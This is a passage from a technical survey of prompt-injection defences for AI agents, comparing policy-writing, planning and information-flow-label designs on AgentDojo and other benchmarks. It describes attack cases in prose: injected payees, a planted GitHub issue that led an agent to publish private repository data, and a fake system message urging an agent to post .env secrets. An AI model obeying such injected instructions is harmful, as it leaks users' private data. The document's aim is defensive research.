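An SMT solver, a program that decides whether any values can satisfy a logical formula, searches for a tool call that the proposed policy P′ allows and the current policy P doesn't. If it finds one, the change needs approval. The agent's permissions can therefore never grow without approval, a property that Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement. But the solver can't detect whether the first policy was too broad, because there is no earlier policy to compare it with.

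*IPIGuard* (An, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) has the model draw a graph of the planned tool calls before it reads any untrusted data. Arrows show which calls need the results of others. In one example, the user asks the agent to find the Slack channel where Alice asked about a coffee mug and to reply there. The model plans three calls, to list the channels, read one and post the reply, and leaves the channel's name blank. After seeing the list, the agent may add calls to read more channels, but it can't add any call that changes something.

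An injection can still affect the arguments the agent fills in for a planned call, for example by supplying a false account number for a payment. IPIGuard tries to prevent this by asking the model to put any instruction it finds in the data into a separate call, which IPIGuard pretends to run and reports as successful. If this works, the model then fills in the real payment as the user wanted.

*DRIFT* (Li, Liu and colleagues, 2025) describes a system that starts with an expected sequence of calls, called a trajectory, and a checklist for their parameters. If a user wants a flight from Paris to London, the checklist can catch an injection that changes the route to London–New York. When the agent departs from the trajectory, the system allows read calls and uses a model to check whether any other call fits the user's intent. If a call fails this check, the system asks the user. Another model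 removes conflicting instructions from tool results before they reach the agent.

### The 15-model study

*CapLite* (Xu, Liu and Nakayama, 2026) tested these four designs on 15 open-weight models. Thirteen were small, with 1.7 to 12 billion parameters, and the other two had 32 and 35 billion. Small models matter because people can run them on their own devices. In each test, a single model did every job, including writing the rules. Each model faced 929 AgentDojo attacks that required a tool call, so each design faced 13,935. The table also includes CapLite, the researchers' own alternative.

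| Design | Successful attacks | Models with no successful attack | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Tokens per run |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 2,322 | 0 of 15 | 59.4% | 50.2% | 28,000 |
| Progent | 676 | 1 | 43.8% | 40.6% | 63,400 |
| IPIGuard | 435 | 2 | 40.1% | 35.7% | 60,500 |
| DRIFT | 214 | 4 | 35.7% | 34.9% | 28,100 |
| CaMeL | 20 | 12 | 24.9% | 27.2% | 93,700 |
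| CapLite | 0 | 15 | 28.1% | 29.0% | 17,100 |

DRIFT stopped every attack on four models, but this is weak evidence that it works, because those models completed fewer than 10% of their tasks under attack. On Llama-3.1-8B, more attacks succeeded with two of the defences than with none, rising from 33 against the undefended agent to 38 with Progent and 71 with IPIGuard.

The counts may also include some harmless cases, since AgentDojo can score a blocked call as a successful attack. Shi and colleagues corrected this error by hand in their own tests of Progent.

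### Failing open and failing closed

An agent's defence fails open when a mistake lets an attack through, and fails closed when a mistake stops legitimate work. Similarly, an electric lock fails open if it releases the door in a power cut and fails closed if it keeps the door locked.

In the 15-model study, Progent, IPIGuard and DRIFT failed open. Progent blocks every call that its rules don't mention, but this default can't help if the model has written a rule that allows too much. The drop in completed tasks from 59.4% to 43.8% suggests that other rules blocked calls the tasks needed.

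Rules that are too broad are hard to notice because they work normally until someone abuses them. *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026) documents this problem in a setting that doesn't involve agents. A model asked for a rule about "the assigned nurse" may write one that admits every nurse. The necessary condition was missing from 60% of the policies that should have depended on who owned a record and from 44% of those that should have depended on a record's status. Checking that the code compiles doesn't reveal such mistakes.

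When CaMeL failed, it mostly failed closed. On eight of the 15 models, more than 15% of runs never produced a program that would run. On Granite-4.2-8B the figure was 68%, because the model returned no code. The interpreter sends errors back to the model for up to ten rounds of repair, which is partly why CaMeL used the most tokens. One run with Qwen3-1.7B made 30 model calls without using a tool.

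CaMeL let through so few attacks partly because some of its programs didn't run, so they couldn't carry out an attacker's instructions. Xu and colleagues had switched off the models' step-by-step reasoning, which may have made correct programs harder to write. CaMeL was also the only one of the four designs with data-flow policies written by people for each AgentDojo suite. The results therefore reflect these policies as well as the kinds of text that the models wrote.

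Larger models did not reliably write safer rules. Within the Qwen3 family, the attack success rate with Progent rose from 3.0% for the smallest model to 14.2% for the largest. Most of this increase occurred because the larger models were easier to attack even without a defence. Progent reduced the number of successful attacks by a little over half in both cases, from 63 to 28 for the smallest model and from 278 to 132 for the largest.

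### Rules that come from the request

Xu and colleagues concluded that small models shouldn't write their own security rules. In CapLite, code derives the rules from the tools' schemas and the user's request, neither of which the attacker can change.

A tool's schema gives its name, a description and a list of its parameters. CapLite treats a tool as read-only if its name and description both start with verbs such as "get" or "search", and as a write tool if either starts with a verb such as "send" or "pay". It refuses to use tools that fit neither pattern. It then classifies a write tool's parameters as authority fields if they determine whom or what the action affects, such as recipients, amounts, file identifiers and web addresses. It doesn't count message text, dates or simple options as authority fields.

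CapLite handles a request in five steps:

1. A planning model sees only the request and the tools' documentation. It commits to a list of write calls and leaves blanks for values it has to look up.
2. A reading model makes up to ten read-only calls to find those values. If a call contacts a web address, that address must appear in the request.
3. Code extracts possible values from the results. A model picks one for each blank but can't write its own.
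4. A model writes any free text, such as the body of a message.
5. Before each write call, code checks that every authority field exactly matches something in the user's request. A request that mentions 100 doesn't permit a payment of 1.

An injection therefore can't add a write call or redirect a planned one to a recipient the user didn't name. Xu and colleagues call this guarantee write integrity, and it holds even if every model in the system follows the attacker's instructions.

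In one test, a user asks a banking agent to change their password, and the account data contains an injected instruction to send money to the attacker. The undefended agent and DRIFT both send the money. CapLite's planning model commits to a single write call, the password change, before anything reads the account data. The reading model later tries to change the password itself, but CapLite blocks the attempt because that model may only read. The committed call then passes the check, so the password changes and no money is sent.

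CapLite can't post the reply about the coffee mug without help, because the user never named the channel. Xu and colleagues traced a similar Slack task, in which the channel's name appeared only in a tool result. No value passed the check, so CapLite returned the decision to the user, while the undefended agent completed the task. When a simulated user supplied the right channel, CapLite finished after one confirmation. But in the benchmark nobody answered these requests, so each counted as a failure. CapLite would also need the user to confirm Bob's address in the meeting notes, whether or not an attacker had changed it.

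Such questions caused only 8–12% of CapLite's failures when no attack was under way. The largest share, 43%, came from plans with missing or incorrect write calls, so a better planning model should help. CapLite's plans also can't contain loops or conditions, which probably explains why CaMeL completed 13.5 percentage points more tasks under attack with Gemma-4-12B, a model that writes runnable programs.

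Xu and colleagues removed parts of CapLite on eight of the models to see what each part contributed. Without the check on authority fields, the agent's task completion rate rose by 5.6 percentage points when there was no attack, but 106 of 7,432 attacks succeeded. When the planning model could add write calls after seeing the results, 53 attacks succeeded.

They also tried a looser rule that could count a file as named in the request if its title matched the user's words. An attacker could then plant a file with that title, and 23 of 103 such attacks succeeded, compared with none of 104 under the strict rule.

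The guarantee doesn't prevent an injection from changing the text of a message to the right person, the date of a payment or what the agent tells the user. Xu and colleagues left 20 test cases out of the attack count because the attacker only wanted a sentence to appear in the final answer, and in their example CapLite repeated that sentence. All the tests used AgentDojo, whose tools have conventional names. A tool called "process", for example, would fit neither of CapLite's verb lists, so an agent that needed it couldn't do its work.

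### What model-written rules can do that fixed ones can't

The case for model-written rules is that they can adapt to what the agent finds. Li and colleagues measured how much this helps by running DRIFT on GPT-4o-mini with parts switched off. With a fixed trajectory and checklist, the agent completed 43% of tasks and 2.1% of attacks succeeded. When a model could approve departures from the plan, the agent completed 58%, but 5.4% of attacks succeeded. Removing suspicious instructions from tool results lowered the attack success rate to 1.4% with little loss of utility. The benefit came mainly from tasks that needed at least three tool calls.

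Fixed plans do worse still on AgentDyn, a benchmark of open-ended tasks in which the right steps depend on what the agent reads. Li and colleagues found that CaMeL completed none of the tasks. DRIFT and Progent also did badly but completed some. CapLite would probably do badly too, since it decides on every write call before reading anything.

The published results with commercial models look much better than those of the 15-model study. All of these come from each design's own developers, using AgentDojo:

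| Design | Agent's model | Successful attacks, no defence | Successful attacks, with defence |
|---|---|---|---|
| Progent | GPT-4o | 39.9% | 1.0% |
| Progent | Claude Sonnet 4 | 6.8% | 0.5% |
| IPIGuard | GPT-4o-mini | 27.2% | 0.6% |
| DRIFT | GPT-4o | 51.7% | 1.7% |
| SARA | GPT-4o-mini | 15.8% | 0.06% |

SARA, from *When Tool Outputs Become Commands*, builds a contract from the user's request that lists the permitted effects. Content the agent reads can fill in details of the contract but can't add permitted effects. SARA kept its attack success rate low without reducing the number of tasks completed under attack. It did nearly as well on AgentDyn, where 0.17% of attacks succeeded.

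Progent achieved its 1.0% even though Shi and colleagues automatically approved every expansion of the policy, to imitate a careless user. When a careful person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, no attack succeeded. Only 6% of policy changes were expansions, so a reviewer would have few to consider. But *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that an injection in a tool result may lead the model to loosen the policy. The solver requires someone to approve such a change, but that person may not notice the attack.

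Narisetty and colleagues, who work at a security start-up, tested Progent independently, using a much weaker model, Qwen2.5-7B, both to run the agent and to write the policy. The attack success rate fell from 25.8% to 4.2%, close to Progent's 4.9% average in the 15-model study. But the agent also completed fewer tasks under attack (27%, down from 45%) and needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. They also wrote an attack that presented the malicious action as a necessary, pre-authorised step, to get the model to add it to the policy. It succeeded only 2.6% of the time, perhaps because the milder wording also made the agent less likely to obey.

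It remains unclear whether a stronger model writes safer rules or only more useful ones. Shi and colleagues kept GPT-4o as the agent and had several models write the policy. The attack success rate ranged from 1% to just under 5%, depending on which model wrote it. When An and colleagues kept a 7-billion-parameter model as the agent and had the stronger o4-mini draw the graph, the share of tasks completed rose from 35% to 52%, but the attack success rate also rose, from 0.2% to 3.7%.

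The strongest evidence for adaptable rules may come from the 15-model study itself. On its largest model, Qwen3.6-35B-A3B, DRIFT completed 77% of tasks under attack, almost as many as the undefended agent, and let through 17 of 929 attacks. CapLite let through none but completed only 46% of tasks. A bank would probably choose CapLite, while someone organising a holiday might accept DRIFT's risk. The commercial models in these tests date from 2024 and 2025, so the results are weak evidence about the rules that the best models of late 2026 would write.

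A model can also draft rules for people and code to check before the agent starts work. In *ActGov* (2026), a model drafts policies from the tools' specifications, records of harmless tasks and successful attacks. A solver then searches for any case in which the draft would violate a fixed set of security requirements, and the system deploys the policy only if the solver finds none. This protects against a careless draft, but not against the omission of a requirement from the set. *ToolGuardian* (2026) likewise acknowledges that its own written rules, which performed as intended on a benchmark, may not cover every tool or workflow.

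## Taint tracking with integrity and confidentiality labels

Progent and CapLite need new rules for each request, because what the agent may do depends on what the user asked for. A rule about the origin of data can stay the same for every request. For instance, a bank might forbid its agents to make a payment after reading text that a stranger could have written. To enforce this rule, the software around the model has to record what the agent has read and who could have written it.

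Taint tracking attaches labels to a program's inputs and passes them on to everything computed from those inputs. TaintDroid, a modified version of Android, used it to detect which apps were sending private data over the network. CaMeL does something similar for a program that the planning model writes in advance. Fides, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, applies it to an agent that chooses each step after the previous one finishes.

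### The label lattice

In the simplest version, every piece of data has an integrity label, either trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label, either public or private. Costa and colleagues order the labels by how much they restrict the agent. Private ranks above public, and untrusted ranks above trusted because the agent has to be more careful with a stranger's text than with its user's.

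When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result gets the join of their labels, written ⊔, which is the lowest label at least as restrictive as both. A lattice is an ordered set in which any two elements have a join and its opposite, a meet, though Fides uses only the join. In 1976, Dorothy Denning proposed using lattices to control information flow.

Two labels with two values each give four combinations. The lowest is (trusted, public) and the highest is (untrusted, private). Neither of the other two is above the other, and their join is the highest label:

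(untrusted, public) ⊔ (trusted, private) = (untrusted, private)

An agent that reads a stranger's public post and then a confidential file is labeled both low-integrity and high-confidentiality, because its conversation now contains text that may be hostile and information worth stealing.

A label can also be a set of people. Suppose that A, B and C may read one document, that B, C and D may read another, and that the agent writes a summary of both. Only people who may read both documents may read the summary:

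{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

The summary may reveal something from either document, so neither A, who can't read the second, nor D, who can't read the first, may read it. The join is an intersection here because a shorter list of readers is more restrictive.

For integrity, the label lists everyone who could have written the data, and the join is a union. If A, B and C can edit the first document and B, C and D can edit the second, then any of the four could have influenced the summary:

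{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∪ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C, D}

CaMeL combines its tags for readers and sources in the same way.

### Two policies

A monitor needs rules that turn labels into decisions. Costa and colleagues give two basic rules. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up from the same group, calls them "trusted action" and "permitted flow".

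Trusted action applies to consequential calls, such as payments. Suppose the model proposes to call a tool with arguments a₁ to aₙ. Let ℓ be the label of everything the model had read when it made the proposal, and let ℓ₁ to ℓₙ be the labels of the arguments. The monitor allows the call only if

integrity(ℓ ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ) = trusted

A single untrusted argument is therefore enough to block the call, as is an untrusted sentence anywhere in the conversation.

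Permitted flow applies to calls that send data somewhere. If R is the set of people who will receive the data and S is the set of people allowed to read it, the monitor allows the call only if

R ⊆ S

Permitted flow by itself doesn't prevent prompt injection, because a stranger's text can still cause the agent to send a message. But the message can only go to people who already had the right to read what it contains. Trusted action by itself lets users share private data with someone new, since no attacker can have prompted the call. Requiring both gives the strongest protection but also causes the most refusals.

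Permitted flow also catches leaks that involve no attacker. In an example from Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered e-mails. One is from Priya, with a preview of the quarterly sales, and another is from Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet. Once the agent has read both e-mails, only Alex may read what it writes, because {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}. The agent can't reply to Marco or Priya without asking, even just to thank Priya. If Priya had copied Marco into her e-mail, the agent could have replied to Marco without asking.

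### Why a simple agent gets stuck

Costa and colleagues add labels to the ordinary agent loop as follows:

1. The system message and the user's request enter the conversation as trusted and public.
2. The application sends the conversation to the model. The model's reply gets the join of the labels of all the messages it received, because nobody can tell which of them influenced it.
3. If the reply requests a tool call, the monitor checks the labels of the call and its arguments against the policy for that tool.
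4. If the call passes, the tool runs. Its result gets the join of the labels of the call, the arguments and any stored data that the tool read. Whatever the tool writes gets this label too, so notes that the agent saves from a stranger's e-mail are still untrusted when it opens them later.
5. The application adds the result to the conversation and returns to step 2.

A failed check ends the run in the formal description, but in the tests the application told the model about the refusal, and the model could try something else. Costa and colleagues show that the loop can stop secret data from passing directly to places outsiders can see, although an observer might still infer something from which calls the agent makes.

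In the simple agent that Costa and colleagues call the basic planner, the model reads every result, and the conversation's label can rise but never fall. Suppose the user asks the agent to summarize the three latest e-mails and send the summary to a colleague on Slack. Reading the e-mails makes the conversation untrusted, so when the model proposes the requested Slack message, the trusted action policy blocks it. The monitor will also block every other consequential call for the rest of the conversation, even if all three e-mails were harmless.

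### Hiding untrusted results in variables

Fides keeps untrusted text out of the conversation. Before adding a tool result, its code compares the label of each part with the label of the conversation so far. If a part would raise that label, Fides stores it in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. The rest of the result stays visible. With a list of bank transactions, for example, the model can see the dates and amounts but not the descriptions, which strangers can write.

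The visible structure can be enough to finish a task. In one test, the user asked the agent to add Alice to the Slack channel with the fewest messages. The channels' names and messages were untrusted, so the planning model received only variables in their place. It requested the messages in each channel, found one list empty, and added Alice to that channel without access to its name.

If the planning model needs something from inside a variable, one option is to send the variable and a question to a quarantined model, whose answer goes into a new variable with the joined label. In the e-mail summary example, the planning model handles both the e-mails and the summary as variables, as in Willison's dual-LLM pattern, so its conversation is still trusted when it sends the Slack message. A hostile e-mail may still spoil the summary, for instance with an instruction to the quarantined model to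 leave it blank.

The agent can instead inspect the variable, which puts the text into the conversation. The conversation then takes on the text's label, and the monitor blocks consequential calls. Inspection is useful when the agent only has to tell its user something. A policy can also treat a yes-or-no answer more leniently than free text.

### Attacks A and B

In the request to send Bob his document, the meeting notes are untrusted because other people can edit them, so Fides hides them in a variable. The quarantined model extracts the document's name and Bob's address from the notes, and these become two more untrusted variables.

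In attack A, the planning model never reads the injected instruction to forward the user's other mail. If it did inspect the notes and obey the instruction, the trusted action policy would still block the forwarding, because inspecting the notes would have made the conversation untrusted.

In attack B, the notes contain a false address. The conversation is still trusted when the planning model issues the call to send the e-mail, so the outcome depends on which other labels the policy checks. The table covers the case in which the real Bob is allowed to read the document.

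| Policy for sending e-mail | Attack B | Honest notes |
|---|---|---|
| The conversation must be trusted | Sends to the attacker | Sends to Bob |
| The conversation and the recipient must be trusted | Blocks | Blocks |
| The conversation and every argument must be trusted | Blocks | Blocks |
| Every recipient must be allowed to read the document | Blocks | Sends to Bob |

For messages, Costa and colleagues suggest the second policy, which lets the agent send text from an untrusted web page, but only to a recipient whose address came from a trusted source. This check stops attack B but, like CaMeL's known-recipient rule, also stops the legitimate e-mail. Permitted flow blocks the attack and allows the e-mail, provided that someone has recorded who may read the document.

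### Labels and policies in the AgentDojo tests

AgentDojo supplies no labels, so Costa and colleagues wrote code around its tools to add them. For confidentiality, they treated an e-mail's sender and recipients as its only readers, although one of them might have shown it to someone else. For integrity, they marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it. For example, if any attack used the body of an e-mail, they marked all e-mail bodies as untrusted.

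This provided a clear baseline, but it also means the labels could not miss any of the attacks in the test. A company that deploys an agent has no list of future attacks, so it would have to judge each source by other evidence, such as whether the mail server has authenticated the sender's address.

The tests used three policies, which simplify the two basic ones:

| Tools | When the monitor allows the call |
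|---|---|
| Making payments, booking hotels, deleting e-mails, changing passwords | The conversation is trusted |
| Sending e-mails and chat messages, creating calendar events, adding text to files | Every recipient may read the content and it contains no untrusted link, or the conversation is trusted |
| Adding people to a calendar event | Both conditions hold |

The rule about links is there because an attacker who controls a website can receive stolen data as part of a web address.

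None of these policies checks whether an argument is trusted, so attack B would have succeeded against the version of Fides that Costa and colleagues tested. The planning model decides to send the e-mail in a trusted conversation, and the second policy allows this even if the recipient is not permitted to read the document. Kolluri and colleagues describe a form of trusted action in which the developer lists the arguments that must be trusted. However, they used the 2025 policies in their own tests, so the results below are evidence about attack A only.

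### Attacks stopped and tasks completed

The main tests compared Fides with the basic planner and with a "variables only" planner, which hides untrusted results but can neither inspect them nor query a quarantined model. The tests used GPT-4o and an attack whose text names the tools the attacker wants the agent to call. The last four columns give the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack.

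| Planner | Policy checks | Genuine successful attacks | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | Off | 152 | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Basic | On | 0 | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| Variables only | Off | 0 | 47.5 | 43.0 | 57.4 | 38.1 |
| Variables only | On | 0 | 48.0 | 44.0 | 56.3 | 35.2 |
| Fides | Off | 21 | 63.5 | 50.0 | 65.0 | 63.8 |
| Fides | On | 0 | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

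Without checks, Fides let 21 attacks through because its planning model sometimes inspected a variable and obeyed the injected instructions inside. Tool Filter, a defence in which the model starts by discarding the tools it won't need, let 20 through. The checks stopped all genuine attacks, even those on the basic planner, whose model had read every injection.

AgentDojo still counted 20 successful attacks against the basic planner with checks and three against Fides. Costa and colleagues read the records and dismissed these. In some cases the monitor had blocked the call, and in others the attack changed only the wording of an answer. A few were actions that the policies allow, such as putting an event with no other participants in the user's calendar. Such an event reveals nothing to anyone, though it could waste the user's time.

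Policy checks made the basic planner far less useful in three of the four suites. Its utility fell from 98.8% to 37.5% in banking and from 93.3% to 20.0% on Slack. With checks on, Fides recovered some of the loss, completing an average of 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic planner across the suites. Travel was the exception, because many travel tasks use tools that the policies allow after an untrusted read. The basic planner could read the results directly, while Fides had to manage variables, which GPT-4o often did badly.

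The variables-only planner did better than it should have because AgentDojo gives credit for lucky guesses. In one banking task, the agent must report the price of a New Year's gift, which it can identify only from the hidden descriptions. Only one transaction was dated 1 January, so the model reported that amount and passed. In some other tasks, the correct response is to do nothing.

Most of Fides's failures were refusals that the policies required. In many banking tasks, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, but the policies block the payment once the agent has read the file. GPT-4o caused other failures by mixing up variable names or requesting data it didn't need. In one Slack task, it requested a list of channels even though the user had already named the right one.

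The model could also complete a task that the designers expected to be refused. One user wanted a new password if any recent transaction looked suspicious. The designers expected the agent to read the transaction descriptions, which would have made the conversation untrusted and led the monitor to block the change. Instead, the model judged a transaction suspicious from its large amount alone. Because it never read the descriptions, the conversation stayed trusted and the password change went through. No stranger's text influenced the decision, but the model relied on less evidence than the user probably expected.

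### Stronger planning models

OpenAI's o1, which reasons at length before answering, used the variables more skilfully than GPT-4o. With o1 and the checks on, Fides completed 64.5% of tasks in workspace, 68.0% in travel, 56.2% in banking and 54.3% in Slack. On average, that was 16 percentage points more than the basic planner with checks, twice its lead with GPT-4o. With the checks off, Fides was 6.3 points behind the basic planner, so hiding results from a strong model reduces task completion only slightly.

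Kolluri and colleagues reran Fides on four models, assuming that a person would approve calls that failed a check. The table compares how many tasks the agents completed with no approvals and with as many as they needed.

| Model | Basic planner with labels, no approvals | Fides, no approvals | Fides, unlimited approvals |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 38.4% | 50.3% | 56.3% |
| o3-mini | 35.5% | 50.1% | 64.3% |
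| o4-mini | 42.5% | 53.2% | 75.7% |
| GPT-5 | 43.4% | 57.1% | 78.9% |

With GPT-5, about a fifth of all tasks succeeded only with a person's approval. Better models raised the figures in the third column much more than those in the second, which suggests that by this point the policies, or the planner's lack of information about them, limited the agent more than the model's skill did.

The planning model in Fides isn't shown the policies, so it may inspect a variable even though doing so prevents it from making a payment afterwards. Kolluri and colleagues also built Prudentia, a version that shows the model the labels and policies and makes it justify inspecting a variable. With GPT-5, Prudentia completed 72.7% of tasks without approval. With GPT-4o it completed only 42.5%, fewer than Fides, so the extra information seems to help only models that can reason about it.

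They also tested Prudentia on WASP, a benchmark that simulates the websites GitLab and Reddit. A web page mixes trusted and untrusted material, so they labelled posts and issues as untrusted and the site's own buttons and text boxes as trusted. Attacks diverted the undefended agent in 15% to 61% of cases, depending on the model and the site. None succeeded against Prudentia, and it needed no approvals. But the users' tasks were easy for this design because they involved only adding a comment or an upvote, which the planning model can do without reading what others have posted.

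The variables and extra queries make Fides more expensive. With GPT-4o, it cost 1.6 to 4.3 times as much per task as the basic planner with labels, depending on the suite. The most expensive suite still averaged about three cents a task, and Kolluri and colleagues had not tried to reduce the cost.

### The GitHub issue that exposed private repositories

An attack from May 2025 shows how integrity and confidentiality labels work together. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an agent connected to GitHub through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard for giving agents access to outside tools. In MCP, a server program offers the tools, and the agent's application, called the client, calls them.

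The agent's user had several private repositories and a public one containing a Pac-Man game. Anyone can file an issue, such as a bug report, in a public GitHub repository. Willison's blog post *GitHub MCP Exploited* quotes the issue that the researchers planted. In it, they complained that the game's author was not widely recognised. They asked for someone to read the README files in all of the author's repositories, which introduce each project, and to add a chapter about the author.

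The user asked Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues. Claude found this one, read the private repositories, and wrote the chapter. It then published the chapter as a pull request, a proposed change that anyone can read in a public repository. The chapter named private projects and revealed the user's salary and plan to move to South America. The client, Claude Desktop, asks users to confirm each tool call by default, but Invariant Labs found that many choose "Always Allow" and stop watching the calls.

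Every call was one that the user had the right to make, and GitHub's server carried them out correctly. Invariant Labs concluded that GitHub couldn't fix the problem by patching the server. The client has to notice that private data is about to leave because of something a stranger wrote. With labels, it can:

| Step | Label of the new data | Label of the conversation afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| The user asks about open issues | Trusted, public | Trusted, public |
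| The agent reads the issues in the public repository | Untrusted, public | Untrusted, public |
| The agent reads files in the private repositories | Trusted, private | Untrusted, private |
| The agent tries to open a public pull request | None | The monitor blocks the call |

The policy in Microsoft's replay of the attack forbids posting in public when the conversation is labelled both untrusted and private. An agent that has read only public material can still reply to an issue, and one that has read only trusted private files can still publish them if the user wants. Claude 4 Opus had not recognised the attack, but the labels don't depend on the model doing so.

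Invariant Labs proposed a simpler rule, without labels, that limits an agent to one repository per session. This would have stopped the attack, but it also prevents legitimate work that uses two public repositories. It also fails if the malicious issue and the secret are in the same repository, as in an example Microsoft published a year later.

### Labels in GitHub's server and Copilot CLI

Microsoft worked with GitHub to add labels to the server that the attack had used. The labels are sent in a metadata field that MCP already provides, so clients that don't support them can ignore them. A developer has to switch the feature on.

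The code's documentation on pkg.go.dev, a site for software packages in the Go language, gives the label for each kind of result:

| Result | Integrity | Confidentiality |
|---|---|---|
| Issue | Untrusted | Same as the repository |
| File in a public repository | Untrusted, since outsiders can contribute changes | Public |
| File in a private repository | Trusted, since only collaborators can change it | Private |
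| Log of an automated test or build | Untrusted, since it may repeat text from outsiders | Same as the repository |
| Published release of the software | Trusted | Same as the repository |
| Draft release | Trusted | Private, even in a public repository |
| Security alert | Untrusted, since it may quote an attacker's code | Private |

Microsoft describes issues in private repositories as trusted, but the package documentation treats all issues as untrusted. The stricter choice seems wiser, because a colleague may paste a customer's complaint into a private issue without checking it for instructions.

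Each result gets only one label. If a search finds issues in nine public repositories and one private repository, the whole result is labelled private because, according to the documentation, the agent receives it as a single block and could copy any part of it anywhere. This is safe but coarser than the labelling in Fides, which can show the planning model the trusted fields of a result and hide the others. Microsoft expects finer labels to make its prototypes more useful.

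The server only supplies labels, so another program has to enforce the policies. GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the command line, does this experimentally. It keeps one label for the whole conversation, raises it after each tool result, and shows the user a dialog when a call breaks a policy. It covers only some of the GitHub server's tools and doesn't yet support other servers. As Microsoft describes it, the client works like the basic planner, so reading one public issue makes the rest of the conversation untrusted.

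For servers that provide no labels, Microsoft released a gateway, a program that sits between client and server and adds them. For each tool, a developer has to specify the format of its results, write a function that labels them, and write or choose a policy. Microsoft's example is a policy for posting in a channel on Teams, its workplace chat system:

1. If the conversation is trusted, allow the message.
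2. Otherwise, look up the channel's members. If all of them may read the message, allow it.
3. Otherwise, ask the user, and list the people who would gain access.

Like the policies in the 2025 tests, this policy doesn't check where the channel's identifier came from. If an agent used variables to keep its conversation trusted, a false identifier could still cause it to send a legitimate message to the wrong channel.

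Microsoft also suggests that developers who don't want to write policies could rely on the annotations that MCP servers attach to their tools. These can state that a tool only reads data, that it may destroy something, or that it deals with the outside world. A client could, for example, always allow tools that read from a closed system and always ask before using destructive ones. But a server's author could make false annotations, so the standard treats them as hints, which clients must distrust by default and weigh according to what they know about the server (Model Context Protocol, 2026). In March 2026, a proposal to add annotations for trust and sensitivity was still a draft.

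### Fides in Microsoft's Agent Framework

The most complete of the prototypes is in Agent Framework, Microsoft's library for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced it in May as an experimental feature, and it works only in the Python version of the library. Unlike Copilot CLI, it has variables and a quarantined model, and it hides untrusted results by default. Developers mark each tool with the data it can accept. For example, they can block a tool from running after the agent has read anything untrusted, or limit it to public data.

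The announcement gives an example of an attack on an agent that sorts bug reports. A public issue describes a realistic build failure and ends with a fake system message. The message claims that a maintainer has authorised the agent to read the repository's secrets, and tells it to open `.env`, a file where programmers often keep passwords, and post the contents as a comment. Microsoft turns off the hiding of untrusted text for this demonstration, so the model reads the message and follows it. Opening the file marks the conversation as private. The agent then tries to post the comment, but the comment tool accepts only public data, so the monitor blocks the call or asks the user to decide.

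The limit on confidentiality protects only the secrets. An attacker could still dictate a comment made up entirely of public text, such as false advice to other users. To prevent that, the developer would also have to block the comment tool after an untrusted read, but then the agent couldn't reply to any issue whose text it had read.

Developers can run the system without blocking any calls. According to Microsoft's documentation, this mode still tracks labels and logs the calls it would have blocked, so a team can see how often the policies would interrupt legitimate work.

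Microsoft lists four limitations. Once untrusted text enters the conversation, everything that follows is also untrusted unless the developer removes it. An approval request shows the tool and the label that triggered it, but not how the label arose. The quarantined model can answer only one question at a time. The system also depends on developers labelling their data sources.

According to the May announcement, the software treated the results of an unlabelled tool as trusted and public, so a forgotten label removed both protections. The documentation gives a safer default of untrusted and public, which it describes as failing closed, although this default fails closed only for integrity. If a developer forgets to label a tool that looks up salaries, the software will treat the salaries as public, and a limit on confidentiality won't stop the agent from posting them.

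## How far taint spreads through models, sessions and other agents

A missing label gives an agent too much freedom, but more often labels spread to data they have little to do with, and the monitor then blocks harmless actions.

In ordinary code, a programmer can see which inputs an output depends on. If a program computes `total = price * quantity`, the customer's name has no effect on the total, so the total doesn't need the name's label. In a language model, however, any token in the conversation may slightly change the probability of any token the model writes afterwards. The only rule that never misses a dependence is therefore to give each reply the labels of everything the model has read, as Fides does. Costa and colleagues concede that this is "sound but may be overly conservative". Security researchers call the resulting excess of labels over-tainting or label creep.

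### What one newsletter can block

Suppose a user sends an agent one message asking it to check the inbox for anything urgent, pay the landlord £600, and move Tuesday's meeting to Thursday. The message includes the landlord's account number. The inbox contains a newsletter from a garden centre. The monitor allows payments, calendar changes and password changes only while the conversation is trusted.

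| Call | Where its details come from | Conversation's label before the call | Monitor's decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read the inbox | The user | Trusted | Allows |
| Pay the landlord | The user | Untrusted, because of the newsletter | Blocks |
| Move the meeting | The user | Untrusted | Blocks |
| Change a password that afternoon | The user | Untrusted | Blocks |

The newsletter contributed nothing to the last three calls, and the payment would have gone through if the agent had made it first. Hiding the e-mails in variables avoids the problem, but only as long as the planning model doesn't need to read them.

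*Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (2026) examines 353 pairs in programs that call language models, each consisting of an input to the prompt and a dangerous operation later in the code. The input's content reached the operation in only 110 pairs, so the cautious rule, which assumes it always does, would be wrong for about 69% of the 353 pairs.

### Rerunning the model without the suspect text

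One way to find out whether the newsletter mattered is to remove it and run the model again. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, built a system that does this in four steps:

1. The model writes a first answer, y, using all the documents in its context.
2. The system tries a less restrictive label, L′. It leaves out every document that L′ doesn't cover and measures how probable y is without them.
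3. If y is still nearly as probable, the model writes a new answer from the remaining documents alone.
4. The system discards y and returns the new answer with the label L′.

If C is the full set of documents and C′ is the set that remains, the system accepts L′ when

U(y | C) − U(y | C′) ≤ λ

U is negative perplexity, which rises with the probability that the model gives to y. The developer chooses λ, the largest drop to tolerate.

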